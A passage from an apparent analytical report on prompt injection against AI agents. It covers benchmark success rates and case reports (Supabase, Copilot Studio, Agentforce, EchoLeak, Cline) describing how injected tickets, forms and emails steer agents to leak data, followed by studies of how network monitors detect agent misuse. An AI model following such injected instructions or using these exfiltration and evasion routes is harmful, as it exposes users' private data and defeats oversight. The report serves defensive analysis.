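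Chang and colleagues had tested the same Qwen model and reported 54.8%. The two teams used different parts of the benchmark. More than half of Lee and colleagues' cases came from an office application that Chang and colleagues left out, and the setups may have differed in other ways too. Forged turns probably do make injections more effective, but part of the increase reported in ChatInject probably comes from comparing them with a weak plain-text attack.

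The usual explanation for forged turns is that the model treats the attacker's text as the user's. Russinovich tested this idea on injections in general by measuring how closely the model's internal state on the injected text resembled its state on a user's turn. On gpt-oss-20b, successful injections resembled user text more than failed ones did at all 12 layers he examined. On Qwen3-30B, the measure did not predict success. The explanation may therefore hold for some models and not others.

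Russinovich also replayed injections that had succeeded in LLMail-Inject, a public competition to attack an email assistant. Only 128 of 2,052 attempts worked on an undefended gpt-oss-20b, so most attacks written for one model failed on another. He says the ones that carried over forged the message format.

Deng and colleagues (2026) automated the search for effective templates. Their software generates many variants and uses the target's responses to decide which to try next, without access to the model's parameters or its real template. On AgentDojo, the attack succeeded in 79.76% of cases on average across seven closed models, including GPT-4.1 and Gemini 3. That is far above the ChatInject averages, though the models were different and the attack adapted to them. The technique also works outside benchmarks. Deng and colleagues examined 942 commercial agents and found more than 70 vulnerabilities,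 which the vendors confirmed.

### Injection rates in current models

Models released in 2026 resist injections much better, at least on tests with a fixed set of attacks. They used to be hard to compare because developers chose their own tests. VentureBeat, for example, lists different injection tests for Anthropic's Opus 4.8 and OpenAI's GPT-5.5. By September 2026, both companies were reporting results on a benchmark from Gray Swan, a security company that runs public competitions in attacking AI agents. Gray Swan developed the benchmark with the British and American governments' AI testing institutes and with model developers.

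Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Fable 5.1 describes the benchmark as 1,804 attacks in 37 scenarios. The scenarios cover coding, other tool use and operating a computer through its screen. Gray Swan selected attacks that had worked on several models. OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026) gives results on a nearly identical set of 1,810 attacks. The figures below are the estimated probabilities that at least one attack succeeds within a given number of attempts:

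| Model | Reported by | 1 attempt | 10 attempts | 15 attempts |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5.1 | Anthropic | 0.1% | 0.7% | 1.0% |
| Claude Opus 5 | Anthropic | 0.4% | 3.6% | 4.8% |
| Claude Fable 5 | Anthropic | 0.6% | 4.9% | 6.5% |
| GPT-6 Astra | OpenAI | not given | not given | 8.5% |
| Gemini 3.7 Flash | Anthropic | not given | not given | 9.2% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | OpenAI | not given | not given | 27.0% |

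Attacks on most of the other companies' models in Anthropic's comparison succeeded between 24% and 53% of the time within 15 attempts, so the choice of model makes a large difference. The kind of task also matters. Within 15 attempts, attacks on Fable 5.1 succeeded 4.1% of the time in screen-based computer use, 0.3% in coding and 0.0% in other tool use. Dana's assistant belongs to the last group, in which the agent acts through structured calls.

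The tested systems were set up differently. OpenAI's figure is for a version of Astra with safeguards switched on. Anthropic's models ran without their dedicated injection filters but with other filters, which pass some requests to an older model. These filters sent 23% of Fable 5.1's test runs to the older model.

The figures also change when the benchmark does. In July 2026, Schneier on Security's *Anthropic’s Opus 5 Is Better at Resisting Prompt Injection* (2026) quoted a rate of 2.0% within 15 attempts for Opus 5 and 20.0% for GPT-5.6 Sol. By September, these had risen to 4.8% and 27.0%. Anthropic's September results include nine new scenarios and 670 new attacks. A rate therefore depends on both the model and the set of attacks, and a newer set can more than double it.

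In OpenAI's internal tests, resistance to indirect injections also improved, from 96.23% for GPT-5.6 Sol to 99.79% for Astra, so the attack success rate fell from 3.77% to 0.21%. TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* cautions that the GPT-5.6 figures are shares of attempts in OpenAI's test environments, not the probability of a breach in a real deployment.

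### How repeated attempts change the rate

If every attempt had the same independent probability *p* of success, the probability of at least one success in *k* attempts would be

1 − (1 − p)ᵏ

In older results, the success rate rose more slowly than the formula predicts. According to The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals*, strong attacks on that model succeeded 4.7% of the time with one attempt, 33.6% with ten and 63% with 100. The formula gives 38% for ten attempts, which is close, but 99% for 100. This is probably because some scenarios are much harder than others. An attacker with many attempts soon succeeds in the easy ones and keeps failing in the rest, which slows the rise in the average.

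Repeated attempts can still raise the success rate by a large amount. VentureBeat reports that in a screen-based test without safeguards, a single attempt against Opus 4.6, released in February 2026, succeeded 17.8% of the time. After 200 attempts, the rate was 78.6% without safeguards and 57.1% with them. In a restricted coding environment, all 200 attempts failed.

The relevant figure depends on the attacker. Someone who wants Dana's price limit might send her several differently worded messages, so the rate for 10 or 15 attempts is a better guide than the rate for one. Someone willing to target any company might send the same message to a thousand companies. At a rate of 0.1%, that would produce one success on average, but the outcomes would not be independent. If the companies use the same model in similar ways, a message that works on one may work on many, and most messages will work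 on none.

Anthropic warns that testing against a fixed collection of attacks can also create a false sense of security, because a model may resist familiar attacks and still be vulnerable to new ones. It therefore also reports results from Shade, an automated attacker that Gray Swan trains to improve its injections. Shade gets 200 attempts at each of 40 coding scenarios, and it has already trained on those scenarios against earlier Claude models.

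In September 2026, a new and stronger version of Shade succeeded in 56.87% of its attempts against Fable 5.1 and 90.93% against Opus 5, with the models' reasoning switched on. It succeeded at least once in 38 of the 40 scenarios for Fable 5.1 and in all 40 for Opus 5. With Anthropic's injection filters on, the success rates per attempt fell to 12.80% for Fable 5.1 and 18.21% for Opus 5. On the fixed benchmark, single attempts against Opus 5 succeeded 0.4% of the time.

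Anthropic calls this a highly permissive test because a real attacker could rarely practise on the exact task. The Fable 5.1 result also partly reflects the older Opus 4.8, which received about 64% of the requests, including all those that led to successful attacks. None of the 2,826 requests that Fable 5.1 answered itself led to a successful attack, but Anthropic's other filters had let these requests through, so they may have been easier to resist.

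Better resistance to injection makes agents much safer overall, but it also gives analysts less reason to trust any one alert from a downstream detector. Suppose a company's agents make a million calls a day and read 1,000 injected texts. If 3.77% of the injections succeed, there are about 38 injected calls, and if 0.21% succeed, there are about two. A detector with a false positive rate of 0.1% raises about 1,000 false alerts in either case. If it catches 90% of the injected calls, the share of alerts that are real falls from about 3% at the higher success rate to about 0.2% at the lower one.

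### Simulated tools and missing monitors

InjecAgent and AgentDojo use simulated tools and invented users. Their tasks are usually short, and every attack case contains a planted instruction. Researchers can therefore compare attacks under controlled conditions, but the results do not measure how often real documents contain injections. A real agent may also have a long conversation history, unusual permissions or a confirmation step that the benchmarks lack, and these could make an attack easier or harder.

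Developers know the benchmarks well, and some have trained their models on similar attacks. OpenAI uses an automated attacker to train and test its models, and it has retired two older injection tests because recent models score too well on them. Gray Swan's benchmark can instead be biased against models that were targets in the competitions it came from. Those models tend to do worse because people wrote many of the attacks against them, so Anthropic leaves them out of its comparison.

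The tests described here also had no security team watching the network or the receiving service. They count an attack as a success once the agent has carried out the injected task, even if a simple rule about new recipients would have flagged the call a second later. Users can't reliably replace such monitoring. Lee and colleagues found that an agent that has followed an injection often doesn't mention it in its reply, although how often varies with the attack and the model.

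Anthropic notes that repeated attempts would increase a real attacker's chance of detection, but that depends on what the company monitors. If Dana's assistant reads 14 injected emails and ignores the instructions in all of them, it makes no unwanted calls. The mail service's log would show only that it opened 14 messages, as it was supposed to. To notice the attempts, the company would have to examine the text of the incoming messages or the tool results in the harness trace.

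## Case reports: attacks on deployed agents

Researchers have also used injected text to trigger tool calls in commercial products, with the same permissions and connections that paying customers use. Most of these cases are demonstrations, but in January 2026 somebody planted an injection in a live software project, the coding assistant Cline. The researchers published much more about how their attacks worked than about the logs those attacks left, so we have to infer some of what a security team would have seen.

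### Supabase

Supabase hosts databases for application developers, and its MCP server lets a coding assistant run queries on them. *Supabase MCP can leak your entire SQL database* (Willison, 2025) describes an attack that the research team General Analysis worked out. The attacker files a customer support ticket containing instructions addressed to the assistant. When a developer asks the assistant in Cursor, a code editor, to list the latest tickets, the assistant reads the instructions and follows them. It reads a private table of integration tokens and copies the contents into the ticket thread as a new message, which the attacker can read by opening the ticket.

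The assistant reads and writes under the privileged `service_role` account. Supabase databases can use row-level security, which limits the rows each account may read or change, so that customers see only their own tickets. The `service_role` account is exempt from these limits.

Supabase's *Defense in Depth for MCP Servers* (2025) disputes that the company's MCP server "bypasses" row-level security. It says the database still enforces the rules, and that the server may run with higher privileges, as it did in this case. This is correct and doesn't contradict the researchers. The database applied its rules properly, as Tymshare's operating system did, and the attacker benefited from an exemption meant for the developer. Supabase also wrote that nobody had reported a leak of customer data through MCP.

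A database log that stores query text would contain a read of the token table and an insert into the ticket table, both under `service_role`. A developer's assistant might do either in normal use. A network sensor would collect even less evidence, because both queries go to the database the assistant already uses, no email leaves the company, and no unfamiliar server is involved.

The content is the best clue, because credentials don't belong in a message to a customer. Data loss prevention software could search for them, but only if the company had it inspect database writes as well as email and web traffic. A rule that nothing from the token table may enter the ticket table would also work well for this attack, but the next one might use a different pair of tables.

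Willison calls the underlying problem a "lethal trifecta": access to private data, exposure to text an attacker can write, and a way to send data out. Supabase's server provided all three by itself. Its documentation already recommended a read-only setting, which would have blocked the write to the ticket thread. But Supabase still considers prompt injection its main concern in read-only mode, since the assistant can reveal data in other ways, such as through a second tool that sends messages.

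Supabase had also tried to make the model more resistant. It wrapped query results in warnings not to follow any commands inside them, tested the warnings on weaker models and experimented with classifiers that look for dangerous text. These measures reduced the risk without eliminating it. The company now mainly advises keeping AI agents away from production data (the live data of real users). It acknowledges in the same post that many people who build software with AI have only one database and develop directly on it.

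Supabase also recommends approving each tool call by hand, but warns that people tire of this and may not see the whole call on screen. Its server can now ask for confirmation before some operations, such as destructive database commands. Supabase describes these prompts as a guardrail that doesn't guarantee human review, because some clients answer them automatically. The check also might not trigger when an agent adds a message to a ticket, since that destroys nothing.

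### Copilot Studio and Agentforce

Copilot Studio is Microsoft's product for building agents, including agents that start work when somebody submits a form. Capsule Security, which sells protection for agents, found a flaw in Copilot Studio and named it ShareLeak (CVE-2026-21520).

The attacker put the injected text in the comment field of a public form. According to VentureBeat's *Microsoft patched a Copilot Studio prompt injection. The data exfiltrated anyway* (2026), the text imitated a system message, making it a forged turn. Copilot Studio joined it directly to the agent's own instructions. The agent then looked up customer data in SharePoint, Microsoft's document and list storage, and emailed it to the attacker through its Outlook connection. CSO Online's *Copilot and Agentforce fall to form-based prompt injection tricks* (2026) lists names, addresses and phone numbers among the data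 at risk.

The attacker needed no account because the agent already had permission to read the lists and send email, so both calls used valid credentials. Outlook's log would contain a message from the agent's usual connection to an outside address. That would look normal for an agent that answers people who fill in a form, since it regularly emails outside addresses. If the agent only notifies staff, an outside recipient is a strong sign of trouble, and a company could block such messages. VentureBeat recommends limiting these agents to addresses inside the organisation.

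In Capsule's test, Microsoft's safety mechanisms flagged the request as suspicious, but the email went out anyway. This differs from the failure that the theoretical argument predicts, because something close to the model had enough information to recognise the injection. When an agent finishes its task in seconds, an alert that an analyst reads an hour later can help with the clean-up but can't prevent the leak.

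Accounts conflict on whether data loss prevention detected the leak in the test. VentureBeat reports that it never raised an alert, because the email went through a legitimate Outlook action that the system treated as authorised. Adversa AI's *Microsoft Copilot Studio Agent Security Risks*, a vendor's risk profile, says the policies detected the leak but did not block it. VentureBeat's account is more specific. CSO Online, which received Capsule's findings before publication, mentions only that the safety mechanisms raised a flag.

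The term "data loss prevention" covers both searches of outgoing content and rules for connectors, the links between an agent and services such as Outlook. Adversa AI recommends connector rules for Copilot Studio. A policy that permits the Outlook connector gives no grounds for blocking an email sent through it. VentureBeat's explanation fits connector rules better than a content search, so the test is weak evidence about whether a search of the email's text would have found a list of customers' phone numbers.

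Capsule found the flaw on 24 November 2025. Microsoft confirmed it on 5 December and patched it on 15 January 2026, and customers had nothing to install. STAR Labs' *CVE-2026-21520* (2026) gives Microsoft's assessment, a severity of 7.5 out of 10 with no known exploitation. The catalogue entry appeared on 22 January. Its description, reproduced in stack.watch's *Copilot Studio Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026), mentions an attacker viewing sensitive information over a network, but not forms, emails or prompt injection. Until Capsule published the details on 15 April, a customer who read the entry would hardly have known what to look for in old logs.

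VentureBeat advises customers to look for signs of an attack in their records from 24 November, the day Capsule found the flaw, to 15 January. Someone else could have found the flaw earlier, so a careful search would start on the day the agent went into service.

Capsule also found a similar flaw, PipeLeak, in Salesforce's Agentforce. The attacker enters instructions in a public form for potential customers, and the agent follows them when an employee asks it to review the entry. It retrieves customer records and emails them out without any sign to the employee. Capsule found no limit on how many records the agent would send. A request for a single customer's details would not stand out in an audit log the way a bulk export would.

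Salesforce had patched an earlier flaw in the same product by allowing links only to trusted addresses. PipeLeak got around that defence by using the agent's email tool. According to CSO Online, Salesforce acknowledged the injection but called the leak "configuration-specific" and pointed to an optional setting that has a person approve the agent's actions. Capsule's chief executive told VentureBeat that an agent whose every operation needs approval is "just a human clicking through the agent's actions." CISO Whisperer's *Microsoft and Salesforce Patch AI Agent Flaws That Could Leak Sensitive Data* (2026) reports that both companies fixed their flaws. VentureBeat, citing Capsule, reports that Salesforce had not closed the email route. VentureBeat's account is more detailed, but the evidence doesn't settle which is correct.

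A patch can also do little more than block the reported injection. In another Copilot Studio case, which the Cloud Security Alliance published, Microsoft issued a fix within two months. The researchers concluded from their tests that the fix was mainly a filter that recognised their injection. Such a filter does not change the agent's permissions, so a differently worded injection that gets past it can do the same damage.

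Capsule announced its findings on the same day as $7 million in funding for a product that checks tool calls before they run, so it had a reason to stress the failure of older tools. Microsoft's confirmation and patch are good evidence that the flaw was real, but the only evidence that conventional monitoring missed it is Capsule's own test.

### EchoLeak and leaks through links

In January 2025, Aim Labs reported a flaw, which it called EchoLeak, in Microsoft 365 Copilot, an assistant that answers questions using a person's emails and files. An attacker could exploit it by sending the victim an email, which Copilot would later retrieve along with other material and treat as instructions. *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration* (Willison, 2025) explains that attacks of this type make the model put private data into the address of a link.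 TechRadar's *Hackers build zero-click attacks in Microsoft Copilot* (2026) describes the version that uses an image. Software automatically requests the image from the attacker's server, and the request delivers the data contained in the image's address.

EchoLeak exfiltrated data without a tool call. Copilot used the victim's access rights to find the material, but its final step was only to write text in an answer, which other software then displayed. A gateway that inspects tool calls would have found no injected call to block.

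A link can, however, leave more evidence on a network than an email sent through an approved service. In the simplest form of the attack, the victim's browser contacts a server that nobody at the company has used before. A sensor can often record the server's name without decrypting the traffic, although it cannot read the stolen text in the rest of the address. If Dana's assistant had leaked the price limit through an image, the request would have crossed the company's own network, which the email to the attacker did not.

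Aim Labs (2025) wrote that it knew of no affected customers and of no setting or user behaviour that could have prevented the attack. According to Fortune (2025), Microsoft first attempted a fix in April but found further problems in May. Aim Labs waited until June to publish.

Microsoft now restricts which sites a browser may load such images from, so newer attacks have other software make the request. On 3 December 2026, the same research team, now part of Cato Networks, published three more ways to get data out of Copilot under the name ReLeak. Infosecurity Magazine's *Three Zero-Click Vulnerabilities Discovered in Microsoft 365 Copilot* (2026) describes them:

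- Copilot put the data in an image address, and Microsoft's search engine Bing fetched the image.
- Copilot created a document containing a link, and a Microsoft background service opened the link while processing the file.
- Copilot ran Python code that sent the data out of an environment meant to have no outside network access.

In all three, the last request appears to come from Microsoft's servers, where the customer's network sensor cannot record it. The Python route also involves a tool call, because Copilot has to run code. Microsoft patched the three flaws between September and November 2026, and Cato knew of no affected customers.

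TechRadar adds that Copilot refused a direct instruction but followed it when the researchers presented it as a routine business requirement. Microsoft's injection filter stopped neither the email nor the leak. A signature for suspicious commands is unlikely to match a sentence that reads like office procedure.

Some attacks combine a tool call with an image link. *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files* (Willison, 2026) describes an agent that could email its own user without approval. An injection made it send the user a message containing external images, and opening the message sent data to the attacker. The data could include OneDrive links that anyone could use to download a file without logging in.

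A monitor that looks for unfamiliar recipients would be unlikely to flag this call. If Dana's assistant did the same, the mail log would show an email from Dana to herself. Her mail program would make the suspicious request later, when she opened the message. An analyst would have to connect the two events, and the request might look like the many image requests that marketing emails trigger every day.

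### Cline

On 21 December 2025, Cline's developers added an agent based on Claude to their GitHub repository to read and sort new issues, which are bug reports or requests that anyone with a GitHub account can post. The harness put each issue's title straight into the agent's prompt, and the agent could run shell commands on a temporary machine provided by GitHub.

According to Cline's own account, *Post-mortem* (Rizwan, 2026), the agent's GitHub credential could only read the code and write to issues. But the agent's job shared a cache with the nightly job that published new versions of Cline. The cache stored files to speed up later jobs. Anyone who could run commands in the agent's job could leave altered files there, and the nightly job would then load them while it held the publishing credentials.

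The security researcher Adnan Khan reported the flaw on 1 January 2026. His *Clinejection* (2026) describes testing it on a copy of the project with his own API key. Claude ran the planted command, which installed a software package, in every attempt. Khan reproduced only this step, but he had used the cache technique successfully on other projects and explained how it would apply to Cline.

Cline did not respond to Khan's report or to several later messages. Khan published the details on 9 February, and Cline removed the agent within about 30 minutes.

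By then, someone else had tried the attack. Bargury (2026), in *Agent Compromised by Agent To Deploy an Agent*, found that an unknown account had opened an issue with an injected title on 28 January, then closed it about five minutes later and changed the title to "user error". The issue has since disappeared from GitHub, but a public archive of GitHub activity kept the original. Khan's test copy had been public, and Bargury concludes that the attacker probably found the method there.

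On 17 February, somebody used a valid token to publish version 2.3.0 of Cline's command-line program on npm, the main registry for JavaScript software. It was available for about eight hours. The only functional change was an added script that installed OpenClaw, a legitimate open-source agent that users hadn't asked for. According to *Cline CLI 2.3.0 Supply Chain Attack Installed OpenClaw on Developer Systems* (2026), people downloaded the release roughly 4,000 times.

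These events are probably connected, but the evidence is stronger for some steps than for others. SafeDep's *AI Agent Cline v2.3.0 Compromised* notes that nobody has publicly confirmed how the attacker obtained the token.

| Step | Evidence |
|---|---|
| Someone planted an injection in Cline's live project | Strong: the archive kept the issue and its title |
| The agent followed the injection | Indirect: Claude did so in every one of Khan's tests, but no trace of the real run is public |
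| Someone tampered with the nightly job's cache | Fairly strong: failures between 31 January and 3 February matched the marks of a known tool |
| The attacker stole the npm token through that job | Likely but unconfirmed: the job held the token, and someone later used it |
| The person who opened the issue published the release | Bargury's inference |

Bargury thinks the attacker was a bug hunter, because the same account had tested another company's project and the release did no damage. That is plausible, but the person remains unidentified.

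The suspected injected call would have been hard to distinguish from the agent's other commands. Software projects install packages constantly, and this package came from GitHub, where the agent already worked. A sensor on the temporary machine would have been more likely to detect the attack later, when the attacker's code contacted an outside server. In the attacker's other code, Bargury found the address of one such server, run by a service that security testers use to receive messages from compromised systems. An alert for new destinations could have caught that connection, but few machines that build software contact only a short, fixed list of servers.

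The npm registry received the unauthorised release, 2.3.0, with a valid token and the correct package name. Unlike the other releases, it had no matching release run in Cline's repository. After the incident, Cline's developers checked old releases against source code and run records. They also changed their publishing process so that each version now carries a signed statement of the run and source code that produced it. Checking for this statement would expose a release like 2.3.0 even if the upload looked normal.

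The incident also shows that a company's assurance that it has fixed a problem can be wrong even when the company has checked. When Cline replaced its credentials on 9 February, it deleted the wrong npm token. It then checked a management page, which listed no active tokens because the exposed one did not appear there. On 10 February, Khan passed on an anonymous claim that stolen credentials still worked. Cline replied on 11 February that it had revoked all the old tokens, but somebody used one on 17 February. Cline then published a frank correction.

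### The Salesloft Drift thefts

The unauthorised Cline release relied on a stolen credential, and credential theft leaves different traces from an injected call. The Salesloft Drift campaign of August 2025 was a much larger case of such theft. Drift is an AI chat agent that companies connect to other services, including the customer database Salesforce. Attackers obtained the tokens for those connections and used them to copy data. Google told The Hacker News (2025) that it knew of more than 700 organisations that might be affected.

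*Widespread Data Theft Targets Salesforce Instances via Salesloft Drift* (Larsen, Lin and colleagues, 2025), Google's report on the campaign, describes attackers who used the stolen tokens to send their own queries to Salesforce. Although Drift is an AI product, the attackers did not need to deceive its model. They counted records of various types, exported large amounts of data and searched it for passwords and keys to other systems.

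The queries did not come from Drift's usual servers. Of the 20 IP addresses Google listed, 18 were exit nodes of Tor, a network that hides where a connection comes from, and two belonged to cloud providers. Google also listed four names that the attackers' software used to identify itself to Salesforce.

If an attacker had instead used an injection to steer an agent connected to Salesforce, most of those clues would be missing:

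| Detail in the Salesforce logs | Stolen Drift tokens | Injected call through a connected agent |
|---|---|---|
| Account | Drift's connection | The agent's usual connection |
| Source address | Tor and cloud servers | The agent's usual servers |
| Name of the client software | Two names that Google labels malicious and two common Python libraries | The agent's usual client |
| Queries | Counts of records, then bulk exports | Anything the agent's tools allow |
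| Timing | Any time the attackers choose | While the agent is working |

The source address is a stronger clue than the client name because it is harder to imitate. An attacker can make software report any client name, and many harmless programs use the same Python libraries. A company that accepted the Drift token only from Drift's own servers would block queries sent over Tor. An injected call would pass the same kind of check because it comes from the agent's server.

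Despite the clues, the campaign did not end quickly. The thefts had begun by 8 August, and Salesloft and Salesforce revoked the tokens on 20 August. The attackers deleted their query jobs, but the logs remained intact, so companies could still investigate. Logs can help stop an attack only if someone is looking for the right pattern while it is happening.

PipeLeak's bulk export of customer records would look much like the Drift exports in the last two rows of the table in data volume, though its source address would be normal. Limiting how many records an integration can read per hour could therefore slow both kinds of attack, but it would not stop an agent that reads one private row and copies it into a support ticket.

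### How often such attacks happen

The earlier example of a company with ten injected calls in a million used a guessed rate, and case reports cannot replace it with a measured one. Measuring the rate would require counting both the injected calls and all the calls the agents made. The demonstrations include neither count and show only that an attack is possible in one product with one set of permissions.

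Researchers usually choose settings where they expect the attack to work. The Supabase attack required a privileged account, permission to write to the database, and a developer who approved the calls or had switched approval off. The Copilot Studio agent could both read customer data and email outsiders. Such settings may be common, since they make agents useful, but a successful test doesn't show how many customers have them. Researchers also have little reason to publish failed attacks.

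Companies need to know more than the number of injection attempts. A program that searches public web pages can find planted instructions, but it cannot detect which agents read them or what those agents did next. It would also miss most of the planted text in these cases, which was in emails, support tickets and forms. Software inside a company can examine those, but may miss an injection written as a routine business requirement.

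Forecasts have similar limits. STAR Labs lists an estimated chance of about 1.4% that the Copilot Studio flaw would be exploited within 30 days. This estimate doesn't measure past attacks, and it is especially hard to interpret because Microsoft had already fixed the flaw on its own servers.

Microsoft, Supabase, Aim Labs and Cato all stated that they knew of no victims. These statements are some evidence that there were none, particularly Microsoft's, because Microsoft runs the service and holds many of the relevant records. But to recognise an attack on Supabase, a customer would have to notice a strange message that its own privileged account had written. In the Agentforce test, the employee who triggered the agent saw no sign that anything had gone wrong. If victims rarely notice these attacks, the absence of reports is weak evidence that the attacks are rare.

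The attacks that become public are probably the more visible ones. The unauthorised Cline release appeared in a registry that anyone can inspect, and Bargury could recover the deleted issue because outsiders archive GitHub's public activity. Company mailboxes have no such public archive, so if the same attacker had used an injected email to learn one figure from a private contract and then deleted the email, an investigator would need the company's own harness trace to reconstruct what happened.

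## Measurements of what network sensors can see

The published case reports contain little network data, but researchers have recorded agents' traffic in test environments. Detection in these tests ranged from none to very good, largely because the sensors were set up to detect different things. None of the studies compared an injected call to an approved service with the call the user wanted, so they are only indirect evidence about Dana's two emails.

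### Beaconing and how RITA scores it

Malware usually gets its instructions by contacting a server run by whoever planted it. It often does this on a timer, which security staff call beaconing. Encryption hides what the malware sends but not when it connects. People browse the web irregularly, so a long series of evenly spaced connections to one server is a reason to investigate.

RITA, a free tool, searches connection records for this pattern. A training exercise from its maker, Active Countermeasures, explains that it takes each pair of source and destination addresses and examines the time between connections and the size of each connection. Sohail describes two measures that RITA applies to the time gaps. If a quarter of the gaps are shorter than Q₁, half are shorter than Q₂ and three quarters are shorter than Q₃, then

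skewness = (Q₁ + Q₃ − 2Q₂) / (Q₃ − Q₁)

median absolute deviation = median of |gap − Q₂|

Skewness is 0 when the gaps spread evenly around the middle and moves towards 1 when the long gaps lie further from the middle than the short ones. The median absolute deviation is how far a typical gap lies from the middle one. Malware with gaps of 28, 29, 30, 31 and 32 seconds has a skewness of 0 and a deviation of 1 second. An agent with gaps of 2, 4, 7, 20 and 45 seconds has a skewness of about 0.63 and a deviation of 5 seconds. RITA combines such measures into a score from 0.0 to 1.0 that is higher for more regular traffic, so the agent would score lower than the malware.

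The gaps between an agent's tool calls can be irregular because the harness cannot send a call until the model has written it, and some calls take much longer to write than others, but this varies between agents. *Towards Traffic Modelling of Multi-Agent Systems* (2026) attributes the timing to features of the workflow, such as how the software schedules agents and whether several work in parallel. In a small test with 60 sessions of each kind, *Verifiable Agentic Traffic Class* (2026) found that agent traffic was more evenly timed than human traffic, although the researchers had designed both kinds of session. An agent that checks a mailbox once a minute could have timing much like that of malware.

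### Sohail's test of MCP traffic

Sohail tested whether common monitoring tools mistake MCP traffic for malware or let it pass. A script generated eleven kinds of traffic without using a language model: human browsing, ordinary automation, two kinds of simulated malware and seven kinds of MCP traffic. It sent requests to a mock server for 60 seconds at a time, at intervals drawn from chosen distributions. Sohail ran each kind of traffic five times under three conditions: encrypted, encrypted with decryption at a company proxy, and unencrypted.

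Suricata, a signature engine, compared the traffic with 44,236 rules from a widely used free collection. RITA, a second tool, scored the connection records, and a score of 0.8 or more counted as a sign of malware.

On encrypted traffic, the sensors recorded only flow metadata, including a handshake fingerprint. The fingerprint showed that the client was a program and not a browser, but it matched nothing in a database of malicious fingerprints. When the proxy decrypted the traffic, the sensors could read whole tool calls, including terminal commands, database queries and file paths. Suricata raised no alerts on either the encrypted or the decrypted traffic. It raised alerts only on unencrypted traffic, averaging 0.25 per run for two of the MCP profiles, and Sohail traced them to a header missing from the test script's requests. RITA gave all eleven kinds of traffic a score of 0.0.

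Suricata correctly raised no alerts, because its rules describe known malware and harmless MCP requests contain none. Decryption made no difference because, although the sensors could read every argument, the collection had no rules about what a tool call should or shouldn't do.

RITA's result is much harder to interpret, because the simulated malware also scored 0.0. Sohail explains that each 60-second malware run produced fewer than 12 connection records, and RITA reports 0.0 when it has too few connections to calculate stable figures. Because RITA detected neither the malware nor the agents in this setup, the test does not show that it catches malware but misses agents.

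Sohail attributes the MCP scores to a different cause, the irregular delays of a model. However, the shortage of connections probably explains most of them too:

- One MCP profile sent requests at a steady machine speed, with no irregular delays, and still scored 0.0.
- In the profile that imitates a single agent, the typical gap was about 4.5 seconds. That allows only about 12 requests a minute, so RITA would have had roughly as little data as it had for the malware.
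- Sending requests faster didn't necessarily help. The faster malware profile sent about ten requests a second, or 600 per run, yet also left fewer than 12 connection records. The script probably sent many requests over each connection, and RITA counts connections. The fast MCP profiles could have had the same problem.
- The single-agent delays were only mildly irregular. For the distribution Sohail chose, the formula above gives a skewness of about 0.17, which seems too small to push a score all the way to zero.

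Knowing how many connection records each MCP profile had would help settle the question. If the single-agent profile had 12 or fewer records, its score is not evidence of how RITA treats irregular delays.

In normal use, RITA has far more data. According to Active Countermeasures' *Intro to RITA v5!*, it examines the previous 24 hours of traffic every hour. The company's *Malware of the Day* describes a test of Cobalt Strike, a real attack tool, set to connect every 30 seconds. Cobalt Strike made 2,859 connections at that interval in a day, and RITA rated the traffic critical. RITA gave the same rating when the gaps varied by up to 25%.

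During continuous monitoring, RITA also checks when a company's computers first contacted a server and how many of them use it. These checks are off when RITA reads a saved capture, and Sohail ran it on stored records after each test, so they probably did not affect the results. They could help detect an injected call that sends data to a new server, even if the agent's timing looks harmless.

A day-long comparison of agents and malware would be a fairer test of whether the two look alike. It would still not measure how well injected calls are detected, because Sohail generated none. The paper's view that a manipulated agent's traffic has the same structure as a benign agent's is therefore an assumption. It is plausible for Dana's assistant, because RITA looks for a compromised computer that keeps contacting its controller, and an injected email does not create that pattern.

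Sohail proposes two changes. The first is a standard label in the encryption handshake to identify agent traffic. Gateways could then apply separate policies to agents without decrypting anything, but both of Dana's emails would carry the same label. The second is a set of inspection rules that parse MCP messages and check for suspicious arguments. These rules could distinguish some injected calls, but only if the company decrypts the traffic and someone decides which arguments are suspicious.

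### Recognising misuse from packet sizes and timing

In *ANT*, Li, Gao and colleagues (2026) ran three coding agents (Claude Code, Codex and Qwen Code) a total of 3,114 times on 20 tasks and captured every packet going in or out. Seventeen tasks were harmless, such as fixing bugs or checking scientific claims. In the other three, the researchers told the agents to write attack code, escape from a restricted Python environment or break into a deliberately vulnerable web application.

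Li and colleagues then trained 13 existing traffic classifiers to recognise the malicious runs. Eight of the classifiers came from research on identifying which website somebody is visiting over an encrypted connection. Each classifier received packet headers, sizes, directions and timing, with IP addresses masked so that it could not memorise which servers the malicious tasks used.

All 13 classifiers were more than 90% accurate, which sounds impressive until one looks at the test set. It held 189 benign runs and 20 malicious ones, so a program that always answers "benign" would be 90.4% accurate and catch nothing. Seven of the 13 caught fewer than half of the malicious runs. The table shows part of the range:

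| Classifier | Accuracy | Recall | False positive rate |
|---|---|---|---|
| Always answering "benign" | 90.4% | 0% | 0% |
| AWF | 90.4% | 15% | 1.6% |
| FlowLens | 92.3% | 20% | 0% |
| TrafficFormer | 93.3% | 30% | 0% |
| Deep Fingerprinting | 97.6% | 85% | 1.1% |
| Tik-Tok | 98.1% | at least 80% | at most 2.1% |

AWF's false positive rate and both limits for Tik-Tok follow from the accuracy figures and the number of runs. AWF caught three malicious runs and wrongly flagged three benign ones, so it was only as accurate as a program that never flags anything.

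Deep Fingerprinting, one of the best classifiers, caught 17 of the 20 malicious runs and wrongly flagged two of the 189 benign ones, using only the direction of each packet. Its recall was 84 percentage points higher than its false positive rate. By the inequality from the theoretical argument, a gap that large means that whole misuse runs and whole benign runs look very different on the network, at least in this dataset. Encrypted agent traffic can therefore contain evidence of misuse.

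How much evidence of misuse network traffic contains depends on the kind of misuse. Four classifiers, including TrafficFormer, caught nearly every attack on the web application but none of the runs in which the agent wrote attack code or tried to escape its restricted environment. Attacking a web application creates unusual traffic because it involves scanning and repeated probing. Writing attack code produces much the same traffic as writing any other code, because the difference is in the text. Tik-Tok and three other classifiers did relatively well on all three tasks. Li and colleagues suggest that agents trying to get around a restriction make extra model calls and change strategy more often.

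These figures are rough because the test set is small. With 20 malicious runs, Deep Fingerprinting's true recall could plausibly be from about 62% to 97%. Its false positive rate of 1.1% would mean about 110 false alerts for every 10,000 harmless runs. Real misuse may also be far rarer than the one run in ten assumed in the test.

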